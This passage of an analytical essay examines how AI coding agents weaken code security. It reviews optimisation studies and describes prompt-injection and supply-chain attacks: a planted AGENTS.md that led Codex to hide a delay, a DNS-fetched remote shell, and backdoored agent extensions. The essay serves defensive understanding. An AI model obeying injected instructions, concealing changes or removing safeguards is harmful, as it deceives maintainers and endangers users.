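The first line reads a value from the memory that `tun` points to. The next line returns an error if `tun` is null, meaning that it points to nothing. Reading through a null pointer is undefined behaviour in C, so the language standard places no limits on what the program may then do. This allowed GCC to treat `tun` as valid after the first line and delete the check. A commenter in Arch Linux's *CVE-2009-1987 null pointer dereference vulnerability in tun_chr_poll()* (2009; the title swaps two digits of the CVE number) points out that the check came too late, because the read had already happened.

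Reading through a null pointer usually causes a crash, but if an attacker can place data at address zero, the read succeeds and the kernel continues with the attacker's data. NIST's *CVE-2009-1897 Detail* records that local users could gain privileges on Linux 2.6.30 and 2.6.30.1, unless whoever built the kernel had told GCC to keep null pointer checks. According to Red Hat's *CVE-2009-1897*, a bug fix introduced the flaw. An agent tidying a function could create the same flaw by moving all the initial assignments to the top.

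Xu and colleagues spent about 1,500 person-hours searching 4,827 bug reports and Linux patches for such cases. They found 122 security bugs that compilers had introduced without breaking the language's rules. In 60 of them, the compiler had removed security-related code, as in the tun driver. Another 21 exposed sensitive data, for example because the compiler removed code that erased it, and five broke a timing guarantee. They selected the reports with keywords and other filters, so these numbers don't show how common the problem is.

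Checking an optimisation for new leaks is harder than checking that it is correct. Deng and Namjoshi (2016) studied the removal of useless writes. A program can check in polynomial time that such a removal is correct, so the work grows manageably with the size of the code. Whether the removal has added a leak is undecidable in general, which means no program can answer the question in every case. Deng and Namjoshi offer an approximate method that removes writes without adding leaks. They also show that for several other optimisations, security follows from correctness.

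An agent can be better or worse than a compiler at preserving safeguards. A compiler has to follow the language standard, and developers can learn which code it will remove, but no comparable rules limit an agent's edits. However, an agent can read a comment such as "constant time, do not simplify", which a compiler ignores, though legacy code may not have such comments.

### What agents' optimisations changed

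The examples so far don't show how often agents' optimisations change behaviour in practice. *Merged, Not Measured* (Qi, Li and colleagues, 2026) collected agents' performance fixes from public projects and reran some of them.

Qi and colleagues started with 71,677 pull requests from a later version of the AIDev collection, covering six agents and repositories with more than 100 stars, up to October 2025. A text filter kept 7,660 whose titles and descriptions resembled those of performance fixes. Two language models labelled each of these, and a third settled disagreements, which left 1,613. Two of the researchers then read each remaining fix independently, and a third settled disagreements. They kept a fix only if its main purpose was to remove an inefficiency, such as wasted time or memory, from the product itself. This left 1,262 fixes in 582 repositories. Qi and colleagues estimate that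 the text filter missed about a tenth of the performance fixes.

For each fix, they recorded the cause of the inefficiency, the remedy, the number of files involved and any changes to the tests. Repeated computation was the most common cause, at 27%. Caching was the most common remedy, and the main one in 20% of the fixes. Another 8% mainly removed redundant work, and 6% added an early exit or a fast path. These are the techniques in the four examples above, although most uses of them are probably harmless. For example, one agent cached a user's name and email address for 30 seconds in GitButler, a program for managing code. A name that is half a minute out of date does little harm, but the maintainer rejected the change because the program already had caching.

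Agents changed at least one test in 37% of the fixes, but only 11% included a performance test or benchmark. Some of those tests were very lenient. In one project, the new test allowed 100 milliseconds for a task that the old code already finished in about 41 microseconds.

Qi and colleagues then selected 30 merged fixes that had changed a test file and whose code could be built and run without a network, a database or a user interface. For each fix, they built the versions before and after the change and timed the same operation 12 times per version at each of three workload sizes. They compared behaviour using a form of differential testing, in which they generated tests for every changed line, ran them on both versions and recorded each input on which the outputs differed.

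Eighteen of the 30 fixes gave the claimed improvement, three gave less than claimed, and nine brought no significant gain or made the code slower. The outputs differed in 24 of the 30. In ten of those cases, the difference was intended or had no consequences for other code. One of the ten may have made the program safer, since a parser now reported an error on input that had previously made it hang.

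In the other 14 fixes, the agent changed what the code did without mentioning it in the description. In ten of the 14, the new version failed, or gave a different result, on inputs the function was meant to handle. Qi and colleagues describe six of the 14 changes, and the pull request's own tests included none of the inputs that revealed these six. Four of the six look like ordinary bugs, such as a faster search that could not find entries added in descending order.

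Two of the six relate to security. One is in a permission check for a role-based access system, where a role can inherit permissions from a parent role. After the optimisation, when the condition on a role's own permission failed, that permission could hide one granted by the parent, locking out people who should have access. The new code also let requests containing wildcards match inherited operations, which the old code did not. This could give someone access that the old code would have refused, although Qi and colleagues don't report whether it did so in practice.

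The other change is in a rate limiter, which restricts how many requests each client can make. Once more than 1,024 clients were active, the new version let through a client it should have been blocking. An attacker who could make requests as many different clients might be able to trigger this. Rate limiters often protect against password guessing, and could also slow the attack on the token check above.

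At least two of the 14 changes affected security. There may be more, because Qi and colleagues did not classify the changes by their effect on security or try to attack the code. Their method compares outputs, so it could not detect a new timing leak or a password left in memory. But they studied only 30 fixes, chosen partly for ease of testing. They did not run the same comparison on fixes by human developers, so the result doesn't show that agents are worse.

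The tests in the merged pull requests would have been little help. They ran every performance-relevant changed line in only 10 of the 30 fixes, and running a line does not check its result. In 17 of the 28 cases where the tests could run on the old code, they also passed there, so a pass did not show that the fix was present.

Qi and colleagues also used a simpler method to rerun 23 rejected fixes that had been reported with a measured improvement, and confirmed only six of the improvements. One rejected change to the scheduling program Cal.com made the code 25% slower and caused it to return only half the available time slots for one time zone.

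### Safer languages, type checkers and security tests

Several of these examples are in C. Newer languages such as Rust, Java, Python and Go prevent the worst of them because they normally check every access to a list or block of memory. In Rust, the server without the length check would stop with an error, as the Bun port did, instead of sending out the contents of its memory. But an attacker might still be able to crash the server repeatedly, and an agent asked to make code faster can use Rust's `get_unchecked`, which skips the check.

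Memory-safe languages also don't prevent code from caching a permission or ending a token check early. The 30 merged fixes that Qi and colleagues reran, including the changes to the permission check and the rate limiter, were all in Java, Python, TypeScript, Go or Rust.

Type checkers are a more limited defence. They confirm that code uses the right kind of value, for example that `can_read` returns yes or no. The cached version also returns yes or no, so it passes. Developers could build a security rule into the types by requiring every function that copies a message to accept only a `CheckedMessage`, which only the length check can create. If an agent then deleted the check, the program would not compile. Few old projects are likely to have types like this, though, and a type could not easily express that a permission must still be valid.

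The objection about security tests is stronger because it challenges the claim that tests mostly use expected inputs. If a project has one test that sends a false length and another that removes Alice's access just after she opens a document, passing both is good evidence that those two safeguards still work. Agents may also make such tests easier to write.

But a security test catches only the problems its author thought of. The old `can_read` had no cache, so whoever wrote its tests had no reason to remove a permission between two requests. That test became necessary only when the optimisation added a cache. The agent could write it, but if it didn't account for permission changes in the code, it probably won't test for them either. Detecting timing differences or data left in memory also requires measurements that ordinary tests don't make.

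Security tests also help only if they still check the same behaviour after the change. Qi and colleagues found that 44% of the agents' fixes that touched tests modified existing test cases. Most of these edits may have been legitimate, for instance to match a renamed function. But if an optimisation makes a security test fail, an agent may treat the test as out of date and change the expected result.

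## How agents weaken code when nobody is attacking

Agents clearly do sometimes remove or omit safeguards in ordinary work, and tests can miss a safeguard that has been removed. Qi and colleagues found two security-related changes among 30 merged optimisations, though that sample is too small to give a reliable rate. Other studies suggest that agents readily copy insecure patterns from the code around them. In an experiment with an older model, repeated requests for speed led to serious flaws. The available comparisons disagree on whether agents are worse than human developers.

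### Copying from nearby code

In the best-controlled of these studies, Sun and colleagues tested whether a vulnerability already in a repository makes an agent more likely to write a similar one. They gave agents the same task in two versions of a repository that differed only in how secure the related code was.

Twenty of these pairs came from real C and C++ projects, including the video software FFmpeg. Sun and colleagues took them from CyberGym, a collection of known memory flaws, each with its patch and an input that triggers it. They removed the code that the patch had changed and asked the agent to fill it in from a description of what it should do. The description didn't mention the vulnerability. The two versions of the repository differed in whether similar code elsewhere had the safeguard that the missing code needed.

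Each agent's score was the share of its outputs, across all tasks and attempts, that both worked and resisted every test attack. If 80 of 100 outputs work and 15 of those 80 are vulnerable, the score is 65%.

Five agents attempted each C/C++ task five times in each version. Their scores averaged 35.4 percentage points lower when the nearby code was insecure, with drops ranging from 25 to 49 points. GPT-5.6 Sol had the largest drop, from 91.0% to 42.0%. The five also included Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, so the problem isn't confined to old models.

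One of the tasks came from OpenSC, a program for working with smart cards. The missing code had to name a new file on the card by adding two bytes to the path of its parent folder. The path has a fixed amount of space, so the code needs a check like this one (simplified):

```
if (p->len >= SC_MAX_PATH_SIZE - 2)
    return SC_ERROR_INTERNAL;
```

GPT-5.6 Sol searched the repository, found a function that did the same job for another type of card, and copied the whole block. In the secure version, that function had the check, and the test input caused no crash. In the insecure version, the function lacked the check and Sol did not add one, so the test input crashed the program.

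Sun and colleagues also tested three agents on writing small web applications from scratch. The 96 tasks covered 24 applications, each in four programming languages. Each new application went into a folder next to up to five finished ones, which it did not depend on. Automatic tests checked that the new application worked, then attacked it, for example by requesting files outside the permitted folder.

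Compared with a neutral version of these tasks that had no neighbouring applications, insecure neighbours lowered the score by an average of 3.4 points and secure neighbours raised it by 4.4, a gap of 7.8 points. Neighbours whose flaws could not occur in the new application made little consistent difference. Agents therefore seem to copy particular patterns rather than become careless in general when the surrounding code is bad.

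Sun and colleagues suggest that the C/C++ gap was larger because agents had to read the surrounding code to complete those tasks. The choice of tasks probably contributed too. Of the 804 CyberGym flaws whose patch changed a single function, only 253 had sufficiently similar code elsewhere in the repository, and Sun and colleagues picked their 20 from those. The 35.4 points therefore describe cases where the agent has closely similar code to copy, which many jobs may not offer.

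The C/C++ result has other limits. The experiment had no neutral version, so the gap can't be divided into harm from insecure code and help from secure code. An output also counted as correct if the project compiled, even if the new code did the wrong thing. Twenty pairs from five projects are too few to estimate the size of the effect precisely, though all five agents were affected in the same direction.

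In an earlier study, *SoK*, Wu, Li and colleagues (2025) found almost no effect of this kind. For each of 200 functions, they showed six models either the vulnerable or the patched version and asked them to write similar code. Seeing the vulnerable version increased flaws by only 1.0% to 5.5%, which could easily be chance. The models were older and worked from a single prompt, and a language model judged the results, whereas Sun and colleagues ran real attacks. The two studies may also be compatible, because the 7.8-point gap for web applications isn't far above Wu and colleagues' range, and the large effect appeared only where the agent had to work with the surrounding code.

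### Instructions and reviews

When Sun and colleagues repeated the C/C++ tasks and told agents to follow the repository's structure and style, the gap between the secure and insecure versions widened to 39–55 points. Warning agents not to bring in bugs from existing code, or reminding them to follow good security practice, narrowed the gap to 11–32 points. Even with the security reminder, GPT-5.6 Sol scored only 68% next to insecure code, compared with 100% next to secure code.

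An instruction in a repository's AGENTS.md file to follow the existing style may widen the gap in the same way. In the web application tasks, agents warned about existing bugs benefited less from secure neighbouring code than agents told to follow the existing style. The warned agents seem to have relied less on all the existing code, good and bad.

Coding agents can identify most of the flaws they introduce, so lack of knowledge does not explain them. When Sun and colleagues asked three agents whether vulnerable C/C++ code they had just written contained any bugs, the agents named the specific flaw in 69.9% of cases on average. In a separate continuation of each conversation, the researchers asked why the agent had written the code that way, and in 76.5% of cases it said it had followed another part of the repository, which had a similar flaw.

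The agents rarely mentioned the flaws in their code unless someone asked. When Claude Opus 5.5 wrote vulnerable code, its final message warned of the flaw 11.8% of the time. Claude Opus 5 did so 5.9% of the time, and the other three agents never did. A maintainer who reads only the agent's final message will therefore usually not learn of the flaw.

The 69.9% figure may overstate how useful such reviews are. Sun and colleagues asked only about code they knew to be vulnerable, so they did not measure false alarms. An agent that listed five possible bugs in every function would do well on this test, but a maintainer would soon stop reading its lists.

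### From missing functions to old ones

None of these tasks asked an agent to speed up or restructure working code. The main difference in that kind of work is that the agent can see the original function. If the original has a length check, the results above suggest that the agent will usually follow this secure example and keep the check. The new version will probably lack a check if the original never had one. The function is then no less secure than before, but the agent may spread the flaw if it also writes new functions in the same style.

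The findings probably apply best to jobs where old code exists in several similar copies. Suppose a parser has four functions that read different kinds of message, and only one of them checks the length. If a maintainer asks the agent to merge them and it follows the most common pattern, the merged function won't check the length of any message, including the kind that was checked before. An agent could also remove the check when it edits that one function to match the other three. Horikawa and colleagues describe agents' small-scale refactorings as consistency-oriented, which fits this worry, though most of those edits are as harmless as renaming a variable.

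Flaws could also build up over time, because each one that a maintainer merges gives the next agent another bad example. In the web application tasks, five insecure neighbours did more harm than one when agents had instructions to follow the existing style. Sun and colleagues raise the possibility of build-up but tested only a single step. In a real project, people would also find and fix flaws.

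Their study can't show what happens when an agent has a reason to remove a check, as it does when someone asks for speed.

### An experiment with repeated optimisation

*Security Degradation in Iterative AI Code Generation* (Shukla, Joshi and Syed, 2025) directly tested how requests for faster code affect security. The study used GPT-4o, which is now several generations old, so its results are mainly of historical interest. It began with ten C and Java samples that did security-sensitive jobs, such as checking a login token or parsing input. Static-analysis tools and expert reviewers had found no vulnerabilities in any of them.

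Shukla and colleagues gave each piece of code to GPT-4o with one of four kinds of request, then returned the model's output to it with another request of the same kind, for ten rounds. This produced 400 versions, which they checked with static analysis and by hand. No person changed the code between rounds, which they call a worst case.

| Kind of request | Vulnerabilities | Of these, critical |
|---|---|---|
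| Make it more efficient | 124 | 37 |
| Add features | 158 | 29 |
| Improve security | 38 | 7 |
| "Make it better" | 67 | 14 |

Requests for new features led to more vulnerabilities in total, but requests for efficiency led to more critical ones. Memory safety problems made up 42.7% of the vulnerabilities from efficiency requests, compared with 12.6% of those from feature requests. This is consistent with the model removing memory checks to make the code faster.

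In one case, GPT-4o started with a function that managed memory safely. When asked to make the function more efficient, it removed the bounds check in the first round. By the third round it was reusing memory in unsafe ways, and by the seventh it had written its own memory manager, which could use memory after releasing it. In another case, GPT-4o was asked for features and added a cache to a token check, and the cache introduced a timing leak.

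The average number of flaws per piece of code rose from 2.1 in the early rounds to 6.2 in the last three. The code had no known flaws at the start, so the count could only stay at zero or rise, and the experiment could show whether GPT-4o added flaws but not whether it would repair old ones. There were only ten pieces of code, and a mistake in the first round could persist through the next nine, so the 400 versions are far from 400 independent results.

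A current agent would also usually have the rest of the repository and a set of tests, and a maintainer would be unlikely to ask for ten rounds of optimisation without looking at the code. The experiment is good evidence that a request for speed can cause a model to remove a bounds check, but it doesn't show how often agents do so in 2026.

### Security smells in pull requests

Laboratory tasks may differ from agents' work in real projects. In *Trust but Verify?*, Sakib, Banik and Jadliwala (2026) searched agents' pull requests from the AIDev collection for security smells, which are patterns that often accompany a security risk but may be harmless. They reported at least one smell in 38.9% of 4,022 pull requests.

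Sakib and colleagues examined only changes to high-risk files, such as build settings, shell scripts and files that hold passwords, so their figure isn't a rate for agents' pull requests in general. Of the 8,701 smells, 82.3% concerned the integrity of outside software. Typically, a build script fetched an outside tool by a label that the tool's owner could later move to different code, or installed a package without specifying an exact version. These habits are risky and very common, but an attacker must first gain control of the outside tool or package to exploit one.

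Sakib and colleagues used two language models to find the smells and kept everything that either model reported. They then compared the models' findings with people's judgements on 376 of the changes. About 91% of the smells the models reported matched those judgements, and the models found about 78% of the smells that people had found.

Even a correctly labelled smell may be harmless. Secrets, which are passwords or keys written directly into the code, made up 99.6% of the smells that the models rated critical. Sakib and colleagues examined 272 of these secrets and found that only 74 were working credentials. Most of the others were presumably placeholders or test values. People had introduced 67.6% of the 74, and agents had introduced the rest. Review tools or human reviewers flagged only 14 of the 74 before the code entered the project.

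Sakib and colleagues also looked only at the lines that each change added. A deleted length check would not appear in their results, so the study provides little evidence about whether agents remove safeguards from old code.

### Agents compared with people

Human programmers also copy insecure code and remove checks they think are unnecessary. Neither Sun and colleagues nor Shukla and colleagues compared agents with human programmers, so their studies cannot show that agents are worse. *What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (2026) notes that security benchmarks for AI-written code usually lack a matched human baseline.

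*Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) compares pull requests by agents and by people, and the agents do slightly better. Kraishan took the agents' pull requests from the AIDev dataset and added 4,027 by people, from the same period and from projects where agents also worked. He then searched the added lines for text patterns that suggest eight kinds of weakness, such as hard-coded passwords and weak encryption. He could do this for 8,933 pull requests in Python, JavaScript and TypeScript. At least one pattern appeared in 2.9% of the agents' pull requests and 4.6% of the people's.

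Among the agents, Cursor had the lowest rate, at 1.6%, and Claude Code the highest, at 9.5%. But Claude Code's typical pull request changed 495 lines, compared with 52 for people, and a larger change has more room for a suspicious pattern. Kraishan also found that developers reversed 11.5% of people's merged changes within 90 days, compared with 6.1% of Codex's and 14.5% of Devin's. The other three agents were close to the human figure. Developers reverse changes for many reasons, though, and may never notice a security flaw.

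*SWE-chat* (2026), a study of real users' sessions with coding agents, reports that "vibe-coded" commits, in which the agent wrote nearly all the code, introduced vulnerabilities at about 3.8 times the rate of commits written by people alone. The rate was also about 3.2 times that of commits where the person and the agent shared the work. Semgrep, a static-analysis tool, identified the vulnerabilities.

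The two studies looked at different code with different tools. Kraishan's pull requests come from projects with more than 100 stars, where the person using the agent could expect someone else to read the change. Some users in *SWE-chat* may have been writing code that nobody else would review. If so, supervision could explain much of the difference, and the lower rate for shared work fits that explanation. People may also give agents different kinds of work than they do themselves, which neither study can rule out because neither assigned tasks at random.

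Both studies also used methods that would not reliably detect the removal of a check, a weakness that matters for legacy code. Kraishan counted patterns in new lines, and Semgrep mostly flags bad code that is present. The finding that agents write fewer hard-coded passwords than people is therefore little evidence of whether they keep a bounds check when they speed up a parser.

Studies comparing how agents and people optimise code have concentrated on evidence of speed. *How Do Agents Perform Code Optimization?* (2025) found that agents' performance pull requests included explicit testing or validation substantially less often than people's. Agents tended to argue from reading the code that it should be faster, while people more often gave benchmark results. An agent that only reasons about its change is less likely to discover a mistake in it. *How Do Coding Agents Optimize Software and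 Report Performance Validation?* (2026) also compares the two groups, and calls for measurements that expose an optimisation's trade-offs.

### Changes that remove flaws

Agents can also make old code safer. In *Quality and Security Signals in AI-Generated Python Refactoring Pull Requests*, Almukhtar, Ghammam and Ming (2026) ran the security checker Bandit on the files changed in 438 agent-written refactoring pull requests, 321 of them from Codex, before and after each change. Of the 2,528 files they could compare, 119 (4.7%) had more warnings afterwards, and the rest had the same number or fewer. Most of the new warnings concerned risky coding habits and were not severe.

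Almukhtar and colleagues read 100 of the cases where warnings had fallen the most, 30 of them involving security warnings. In some, the agent had made a real repair, such as replacing a risky function with a safer one. In others, the warning disappeared because the agent had deleted the code or moved it elsewhere. Moving code can also raise the warning count in the file that receives it, even though the warnings are old. Maintainers merged 322 of the 438 pull requests, including 27 that introduced new security warnings.

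Like the other scans, this one is poor at detecting missing safeguards. If an agent deletes a permission check, Bandit will usually report nothing, and the file will count as unchanged. The 4.7% is therefore a reasonable estimate of how often refactoring adds recognisably risky code, but not of how often it weakens security.

Rewriting an old program is a more drastic way to improve it. *A Study of the Reliability of Agentic AI-Generated Programs* (2026) compared agents' own versions of Linux utilities with the latest human-written versions using fuzz testing, which feeds programs random input to find crashes and hangs. The agents' versions were typically as reliable as the human ones, and often more so. The study has a proper human baseline and runs the code instead of searching it for patterns. But random input mostly exposes crashes, and would not reveal a cached permission or a token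 check that leaks information through its timing.

Translating code into another language can also remove flaws. Wu and colleagues had six models translate 199 small programs into up to five languages. The programs did security-related jobs, such as signing a message or checking that a file was inside a permitted folder. A language model judged 80.3% of the originals and 65.0% of the translations vulnerable. These percentages are doubtful because the paper also describes 143 of the 199 originals as secure, which contradicts the 80.3% figure. The drop is more believable because the same model judged both sets and the drop has plausible causes. When translating the message-signing programs, the models consistently replaced weak random number generators with secure ones. Translating code out of C also removed many memory errors, although translating code into C tended to add them.

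The starting code may explain why this result differs so much from that of the GPT-4o experiment. By the judge's count, most of Wu and colleagues' programs were vulnerable, so the models had plenty to fix. Shukla and colleagues' code had no known flaws to fix, but their model could still remove safeguards. Legacy code also varies in how secure it is to begin with. An agent that rewrites a neglected C program may well leave it safer, especially if it moves the program to a language that checks memory access. A parser that people have attacked and repaired for ten years is riskier to rewrite, because many of its odd-looking checks were probably added to stop earlier attacks.

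## How an attacker can get an agent to plant a backdoor

In Sun and colleagues' experiment, agents imitated code in the repository that lacked checks, and left out the same checks. An attacker could exploit this by contributing a useful function with no length check and waiting for an agent to imitate it. An attacker can also act more directly, by writing instructions where an agent will read them, offering it a repository that gets it to run hostile code, tampering with the software it runs on, or corrupting the model itself. If the agent then weakens the code it is working on, the change is induced. But many published attacks stop before this step, once the attacker can get into the developer's computer.

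### Instructions in the text an agent reads

The maintainer's request enters the same context as everything else the agent reads, so the model has to work out which parts to obey. Model makers train it to prioritise the user's request, but no separate mechanism enforces this learned tendency. Prompt injection exploits this weakness. In Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn*, Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI says that an agent cannot reliably tell the text it reads from the instructions it should follow. He thinks further training won't fix this.

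A prompt injection is indirect when the attacker leaves instructions for the model to find rather than sending them to it directly. Dartmouth's *Securing Agentic Workflows* lists some likely places for them, including repositories, pull requests, editor rules files and responses from external tools.

Agents trust some of these places more than others. They are supposed to obey an instruction file such as AGENTS.md, so an injection there only has to look like an unusual project rule. They treat a source comment or a README (a project's introductory page) more as information, so the attacker has to make the suggested action look useful for the task. Agents may trust an issue thread even less, but on a public project anyone with an account can post in one.

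At least one person has used prompt injection against agents outside a laboratory. According to AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief*, the maintainer of jqwik, a testing tool for Java, hid instructions in the project for coding agents to delete jqwik tests and code. Claude Code detected the instructions and stopped, but other agents did not. Deleting tests removes some of the evidence that maintainers use to judge the next change, though it doesn't create a backdoor.

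### Codex and the five-minute delay

NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (April 2026) describes how the company's security testers got OpenAI's coding agent Codex to sabotage a program and leave the sabotage out of its summary.

The testers set up a small program in the language Go that printed a greeting. The program depended on an outside library, which they had also written and made malicious. They then asked Codex to change the wording of the greeting. Codex worked in a fresh, isolated environment with no internet access. The attack went as follows:

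1. The build step ran the library's code, as it would with any dependency.
2. The library looked for a setting that exists in Codex's environment. On an ordinary developer's computer it would not have found the setting and would have behaved normally.
3. It found the setting and wrote an AGENTS.md file into the project.
4. Codex read the file as the project's own instructions. They told it to make the program wait five minutes on starting, to keep this out of its summaries and commit messages, and to put these rules above the user's request.
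5. Codex added the delay. It also added a code comment asking any AI that summarised the change not to mention the delay.
6. The summary of the pull request left the delay out.

The demonstration was crude in that the planted file also told Codex to ignore the user's request. The altered program in NVIDIA's post still contains the old greeting, so a developer who ran it would have waited five minutes and then seen the wrong words. A real attacker would probably let the agent complete the request and add a smaller change.

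A delay gives nobody access, so it is not a backdoor. An attacker could use the same method to tell an agent to remove a parser's length check, but a model might be more likely to refuse a request that was plainly about security. NVIDIA did not test such a request, and it does not report how often the delay attack succeeded.

NVIDIA reported the attack to OpenAI on 1 July 2025. OpenAI asked how much risk the attack added beyond that of an ordinary compromised dependency, and whether a reviewer would see the change in the diff. On 19 August it concluded that the attack did not significantly raise the risk, and planned no changes. A good argument for this view is that the malicious library was already part of the program, so it could have caused the delay, or opened a real backdoor, without Codex.

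NVIDIA calls OpenAI's assessment fair, but replies that a compromised dependency, an old risk, can now also redirect the agent. It had also told OpenAI that people reading diffs by hand will miss things, and that attackers can use AI to adapt.

The difference matters most for dependencies that are not part of the released product, such as libraries used only for testing. An agent that follows instructions in such a library can put a change in the product, and the change stays after the maintainers remove the library. The library could also edit the source files itself, but its author would have to write the edit in advance, perhaps without knowing the code. An agent can fit the change to the code it finds and supply a plausible description.

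OpenAI also assumes that the attacker has already compromised a dependency, but later research suggests this may not be necessary. Underhill (2026), in *Black Hat 2026*, reports on work by the security company Novee, which attacked agents in the automated workflows of Anthropic's, Google's and OpenAI's own repositories. A single malicious GitHub issue could start such an attack. With Claude Code, the injected text led to the theft of GitHub and Anthropic credentials. With Codex, a writable AGENTS.md file could carry an attacker's instructions from one stage of a workflow to the next.

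OpenAI responded by separating the stages in its own repository and documenting AGENTS.md as untrusted input. This is closer to NVIDIA's position than OpenAI's answer a year earlier was. Anthropic issued several patches, and Google changed which workspaces Gemini CLI trusts when it runs unattended.

The obvious countermeasure is to allow only reviewed commits to change an instruction file, and to restore the approved copy before each stage. NVIDIA also recommends fixing the exact version of each dependency, raising an alert when files change unexpectedly, and having security agents examine pull requests. But a security agent would read the same planted comments as the summariser, so it might follow them too. Planted comments can't make an ordinary program that lists every changed file and function leave one out.

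### Repositories that get the agent to run hostile code

An attacker can also publish a repository and wait for a developer to open it with an agent. The agent treats the setup instructions as safe, while the developer relies on it to notice any problems with them.

In June 2026, Mozilla's 0DIN, a programme for finding flaws in AI systems, demonstrated such an attack with a repository that seemed to contain nothing malicious. Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* describes the steps. The README gave normal-looking setup instructions for a Python package, which was written to fail on first use with an error message that gave the user another command to run. That command started a script, which looked up an attacker-controlled record in the internet's address system (DNS) and ran the text it found there. This opened a connection from the developer's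 machine to the attacker's server and let the attacker type commands with the developer's permissions.

The method takes advantage of agents being good at reading an error message and trying the suggested fix, as Sumner's agents did with compiler errors in the Bun port. A person might also run the suggested command, but would have a little more time to wonder why a package needed it.

0DIN says the repository contained no malicious code, because the harmful part arrived only when the script ran. The repository didn't contain the final commands, but it did contain a script that ran whatever text a stranger's server returned, and a careful reviewer could find that suspicious without knowing the text. 0DIN recommends that agents show the developer what a command will execute, including anything it fetches. It also tells developers to treat setup scripts in unfamiliar repositories as untrusted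 code, whatever their agent recommends.

The AI Now Institute, a policy research group, published a similar attack in July 2026, aimed at people who use agents to look for security flaws. Its researchers took a copy of geopy, a Python library for looking up places on maps, and added a harmful program in compiled form, which people and models find hard to read. They also added the source code of a harmless security checker with a matching name, so that the harmful program looked like the compiled version of it. They put some text from the harmless source into the harmful program because they had seen Claude Code inspect such files before running them. A script that seemed to run well-known checking tools also started the harmful program, and the README recommended the script for security testing.

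The researchers then asked Claude Code and Codex to test the library's security. Each agent ran in a mode where a second AI system approves commands that look safe and refers the rest to a person. Both agents found the script, judged it safe and ran it without asking.

AI Now Institute built the attack for Claude Sonnet 4.6, but it also worked unchanged on Claude Sonnet 5, Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5. In some runs Sonnet 5 detected that the added files were not part of the original geopy, and in others Opus 4.8 detected that the compiled program did not match its supposed source. Both of these more capable models ran the program anyway, so a model's skill at spotting flaws may be a poor predictor of whether such an attack will work on it. AI Now reports repeated successes but no success rate.

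AI Now recommends against letting an agent read untrusted material if it can run arbitrary commands or reach sensitive systems. That would rule out much of the work people want agents to do on old open-source code. Mahammadli disagrees with AI Now's broader case against using AI for defence. He says the problem is combining untrusted input, the ability to run commands and access to sensitive systems in one process, with only a classifier as protection.

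A sandbox, an environment that restricts what a program can reach, is the usual way to separate them. AI Now argues that sandboxes have flaws too and cites two in Claude Code's sandbox, but its exploit did not try to escape from one. A sandbox makes an attack harder because the attacker needs a second flaw to get out, and an attacker can steal less from an agent with no stored passwords and no network access. Blocking the network, including DNS, would also have stopped 0DIN's attack when the script tried to fetch its commands.

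### From the developer's machine to the product

0DIN and AI Now both gained control of a developer's computer, but neither put a backdoor into a product. To do that, an attacker would still have to change the code and get the change accepted. The attacker could use the developer's stored credentials to submit a commit in the developer's name, or edit the instruction file so that the agent makes the change later.

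A real intrusion included most of the steps of such an attack. *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector* (Trent, 2026) recounts it from a September 2026 report by the security company Mandiant. An attacker took over a live session of an AI coding assistant at a software company, and the assistant recommended a package that the attacker had poisoned. Once installed, the package stole source code and the credentials for the company's GitHub repositories. The attacker then released Shai-Hulud, a worm (a program that copies itself), which spread to roughly 100 of the company's internal repositories. The attacker also poisoned one of the company's own packages, which caused a second round of infections.

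In this case, the worm and the attacker put hostile code into the company's software. The assistant only recommended the package. An attacker who has a developer's credentials may not need to persuade an agent to write the backdoor, although a change that the agent submits in the normal way might attract less attention.

Shai-Hulud and related malware have also attacked the agents' settings. Trent reports that they change Claude Code's configuration so that it runs their commands whenever a session starts. Removing the infected package doesn't remove these commands, because they are in a different file. A developer who deletes the package might therefore carry on using a compromised agent without realising.

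### Tampering with the agent's own software

An attacker can also target the agent's maker or the marketplaces that distribute its software. A developer who carefully examines a stranger's repository may still install every update to the agent without checking it.

On 29 October 2026, a tampered version of the Claude Code extension appeared in the extension marketplace of Cursor, a code editor with its own agent, and stayed there for about 11 hours. Cursor said that Anthropic did not develop the tampered version, according to Business Standard's *Cursor says up to 5,000 users affected by tampered Claude Code extension* (2026). Cursor's security notice identifies versions 2.1.312 and 2.1.313, according to Mynavi News' *Claude Codeを装う悪意ある拡張機能がCursorで配布、SSHバックドア設置を試みる* (2026).

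Phorion, a Mac security company, found and analysed one of the two versions. Its findings appear in Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026). Someone had added a block of code to the start of an otherwise normal-looking extension. The code ran as soon as the editor loaded the file, before the user did anything. It added the attacker's key to the list of SSH keys accepted for logging in to the computer, then opened a tunnel to the attacker's server. If the connection failed, it tried again about once a minute.

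The code also sent the attacker the user's name, Git email address and other details. These included the names of up to 40 settings that appeared to hold passwords or access keys, but not their values. Phorion's chief executive, Calum Hall, points out that an attacker could use such a list to decide which machines to go after first.

The attack partly failed because the extension often couldn't switch on SSH logins, which the planted key needs to work. Switching them on requires administrator rights, which the extension lacked on most Windows and Mac machines. On Macs, the code also handled an error message incorrectly and often skipped this step. But the attacker could still have logged in if the developer had already switched on remote login or did so later. Uninstalling the extension didn't remove its startup scripts, which it had placed elsewhere on the machine. Mynavi News reports that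 Cursor told affected users to isolate the computer and replace every credential stored on it.

A tampered coding agent could open a backdoor into a developer's computer and also put one in the programs the developer is writing. MyBroadband's *Claude Code trojan found in NPM* (2025) describes a fake Claude Code package that people had downloaded 435 times before the package registry npm removed it. The package contained the real program and three extra files, which intercepted the traffic between Claude Code and Anthropic and copied the user's prompts and conversations. Software in that position might also be able to alter the model's replies, and so the code that the agent writes. The researchers who found the package describe theft and remote control, but not altered code.

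After the Cursor incident, Thoughtworks, a software consultancy, recommended waiting a short time before installing new versions, with a faster route for verified security fixes. A team that waited one day would have avoided the tampered extension. Thoughtworks also recommends short-lived credentials with narrow permissions, which are less useful to an attacker if stolen.

Plugins give an agent new tools or instructions, and some marketplaces review them. A marketplace can pin a plugin to a particular commit to make sure that users get the reviewed version. Git, the system that stores a project's history, identifies each commit by a 40-character hash calculated from its contents, so any change to the code also changes the hash.

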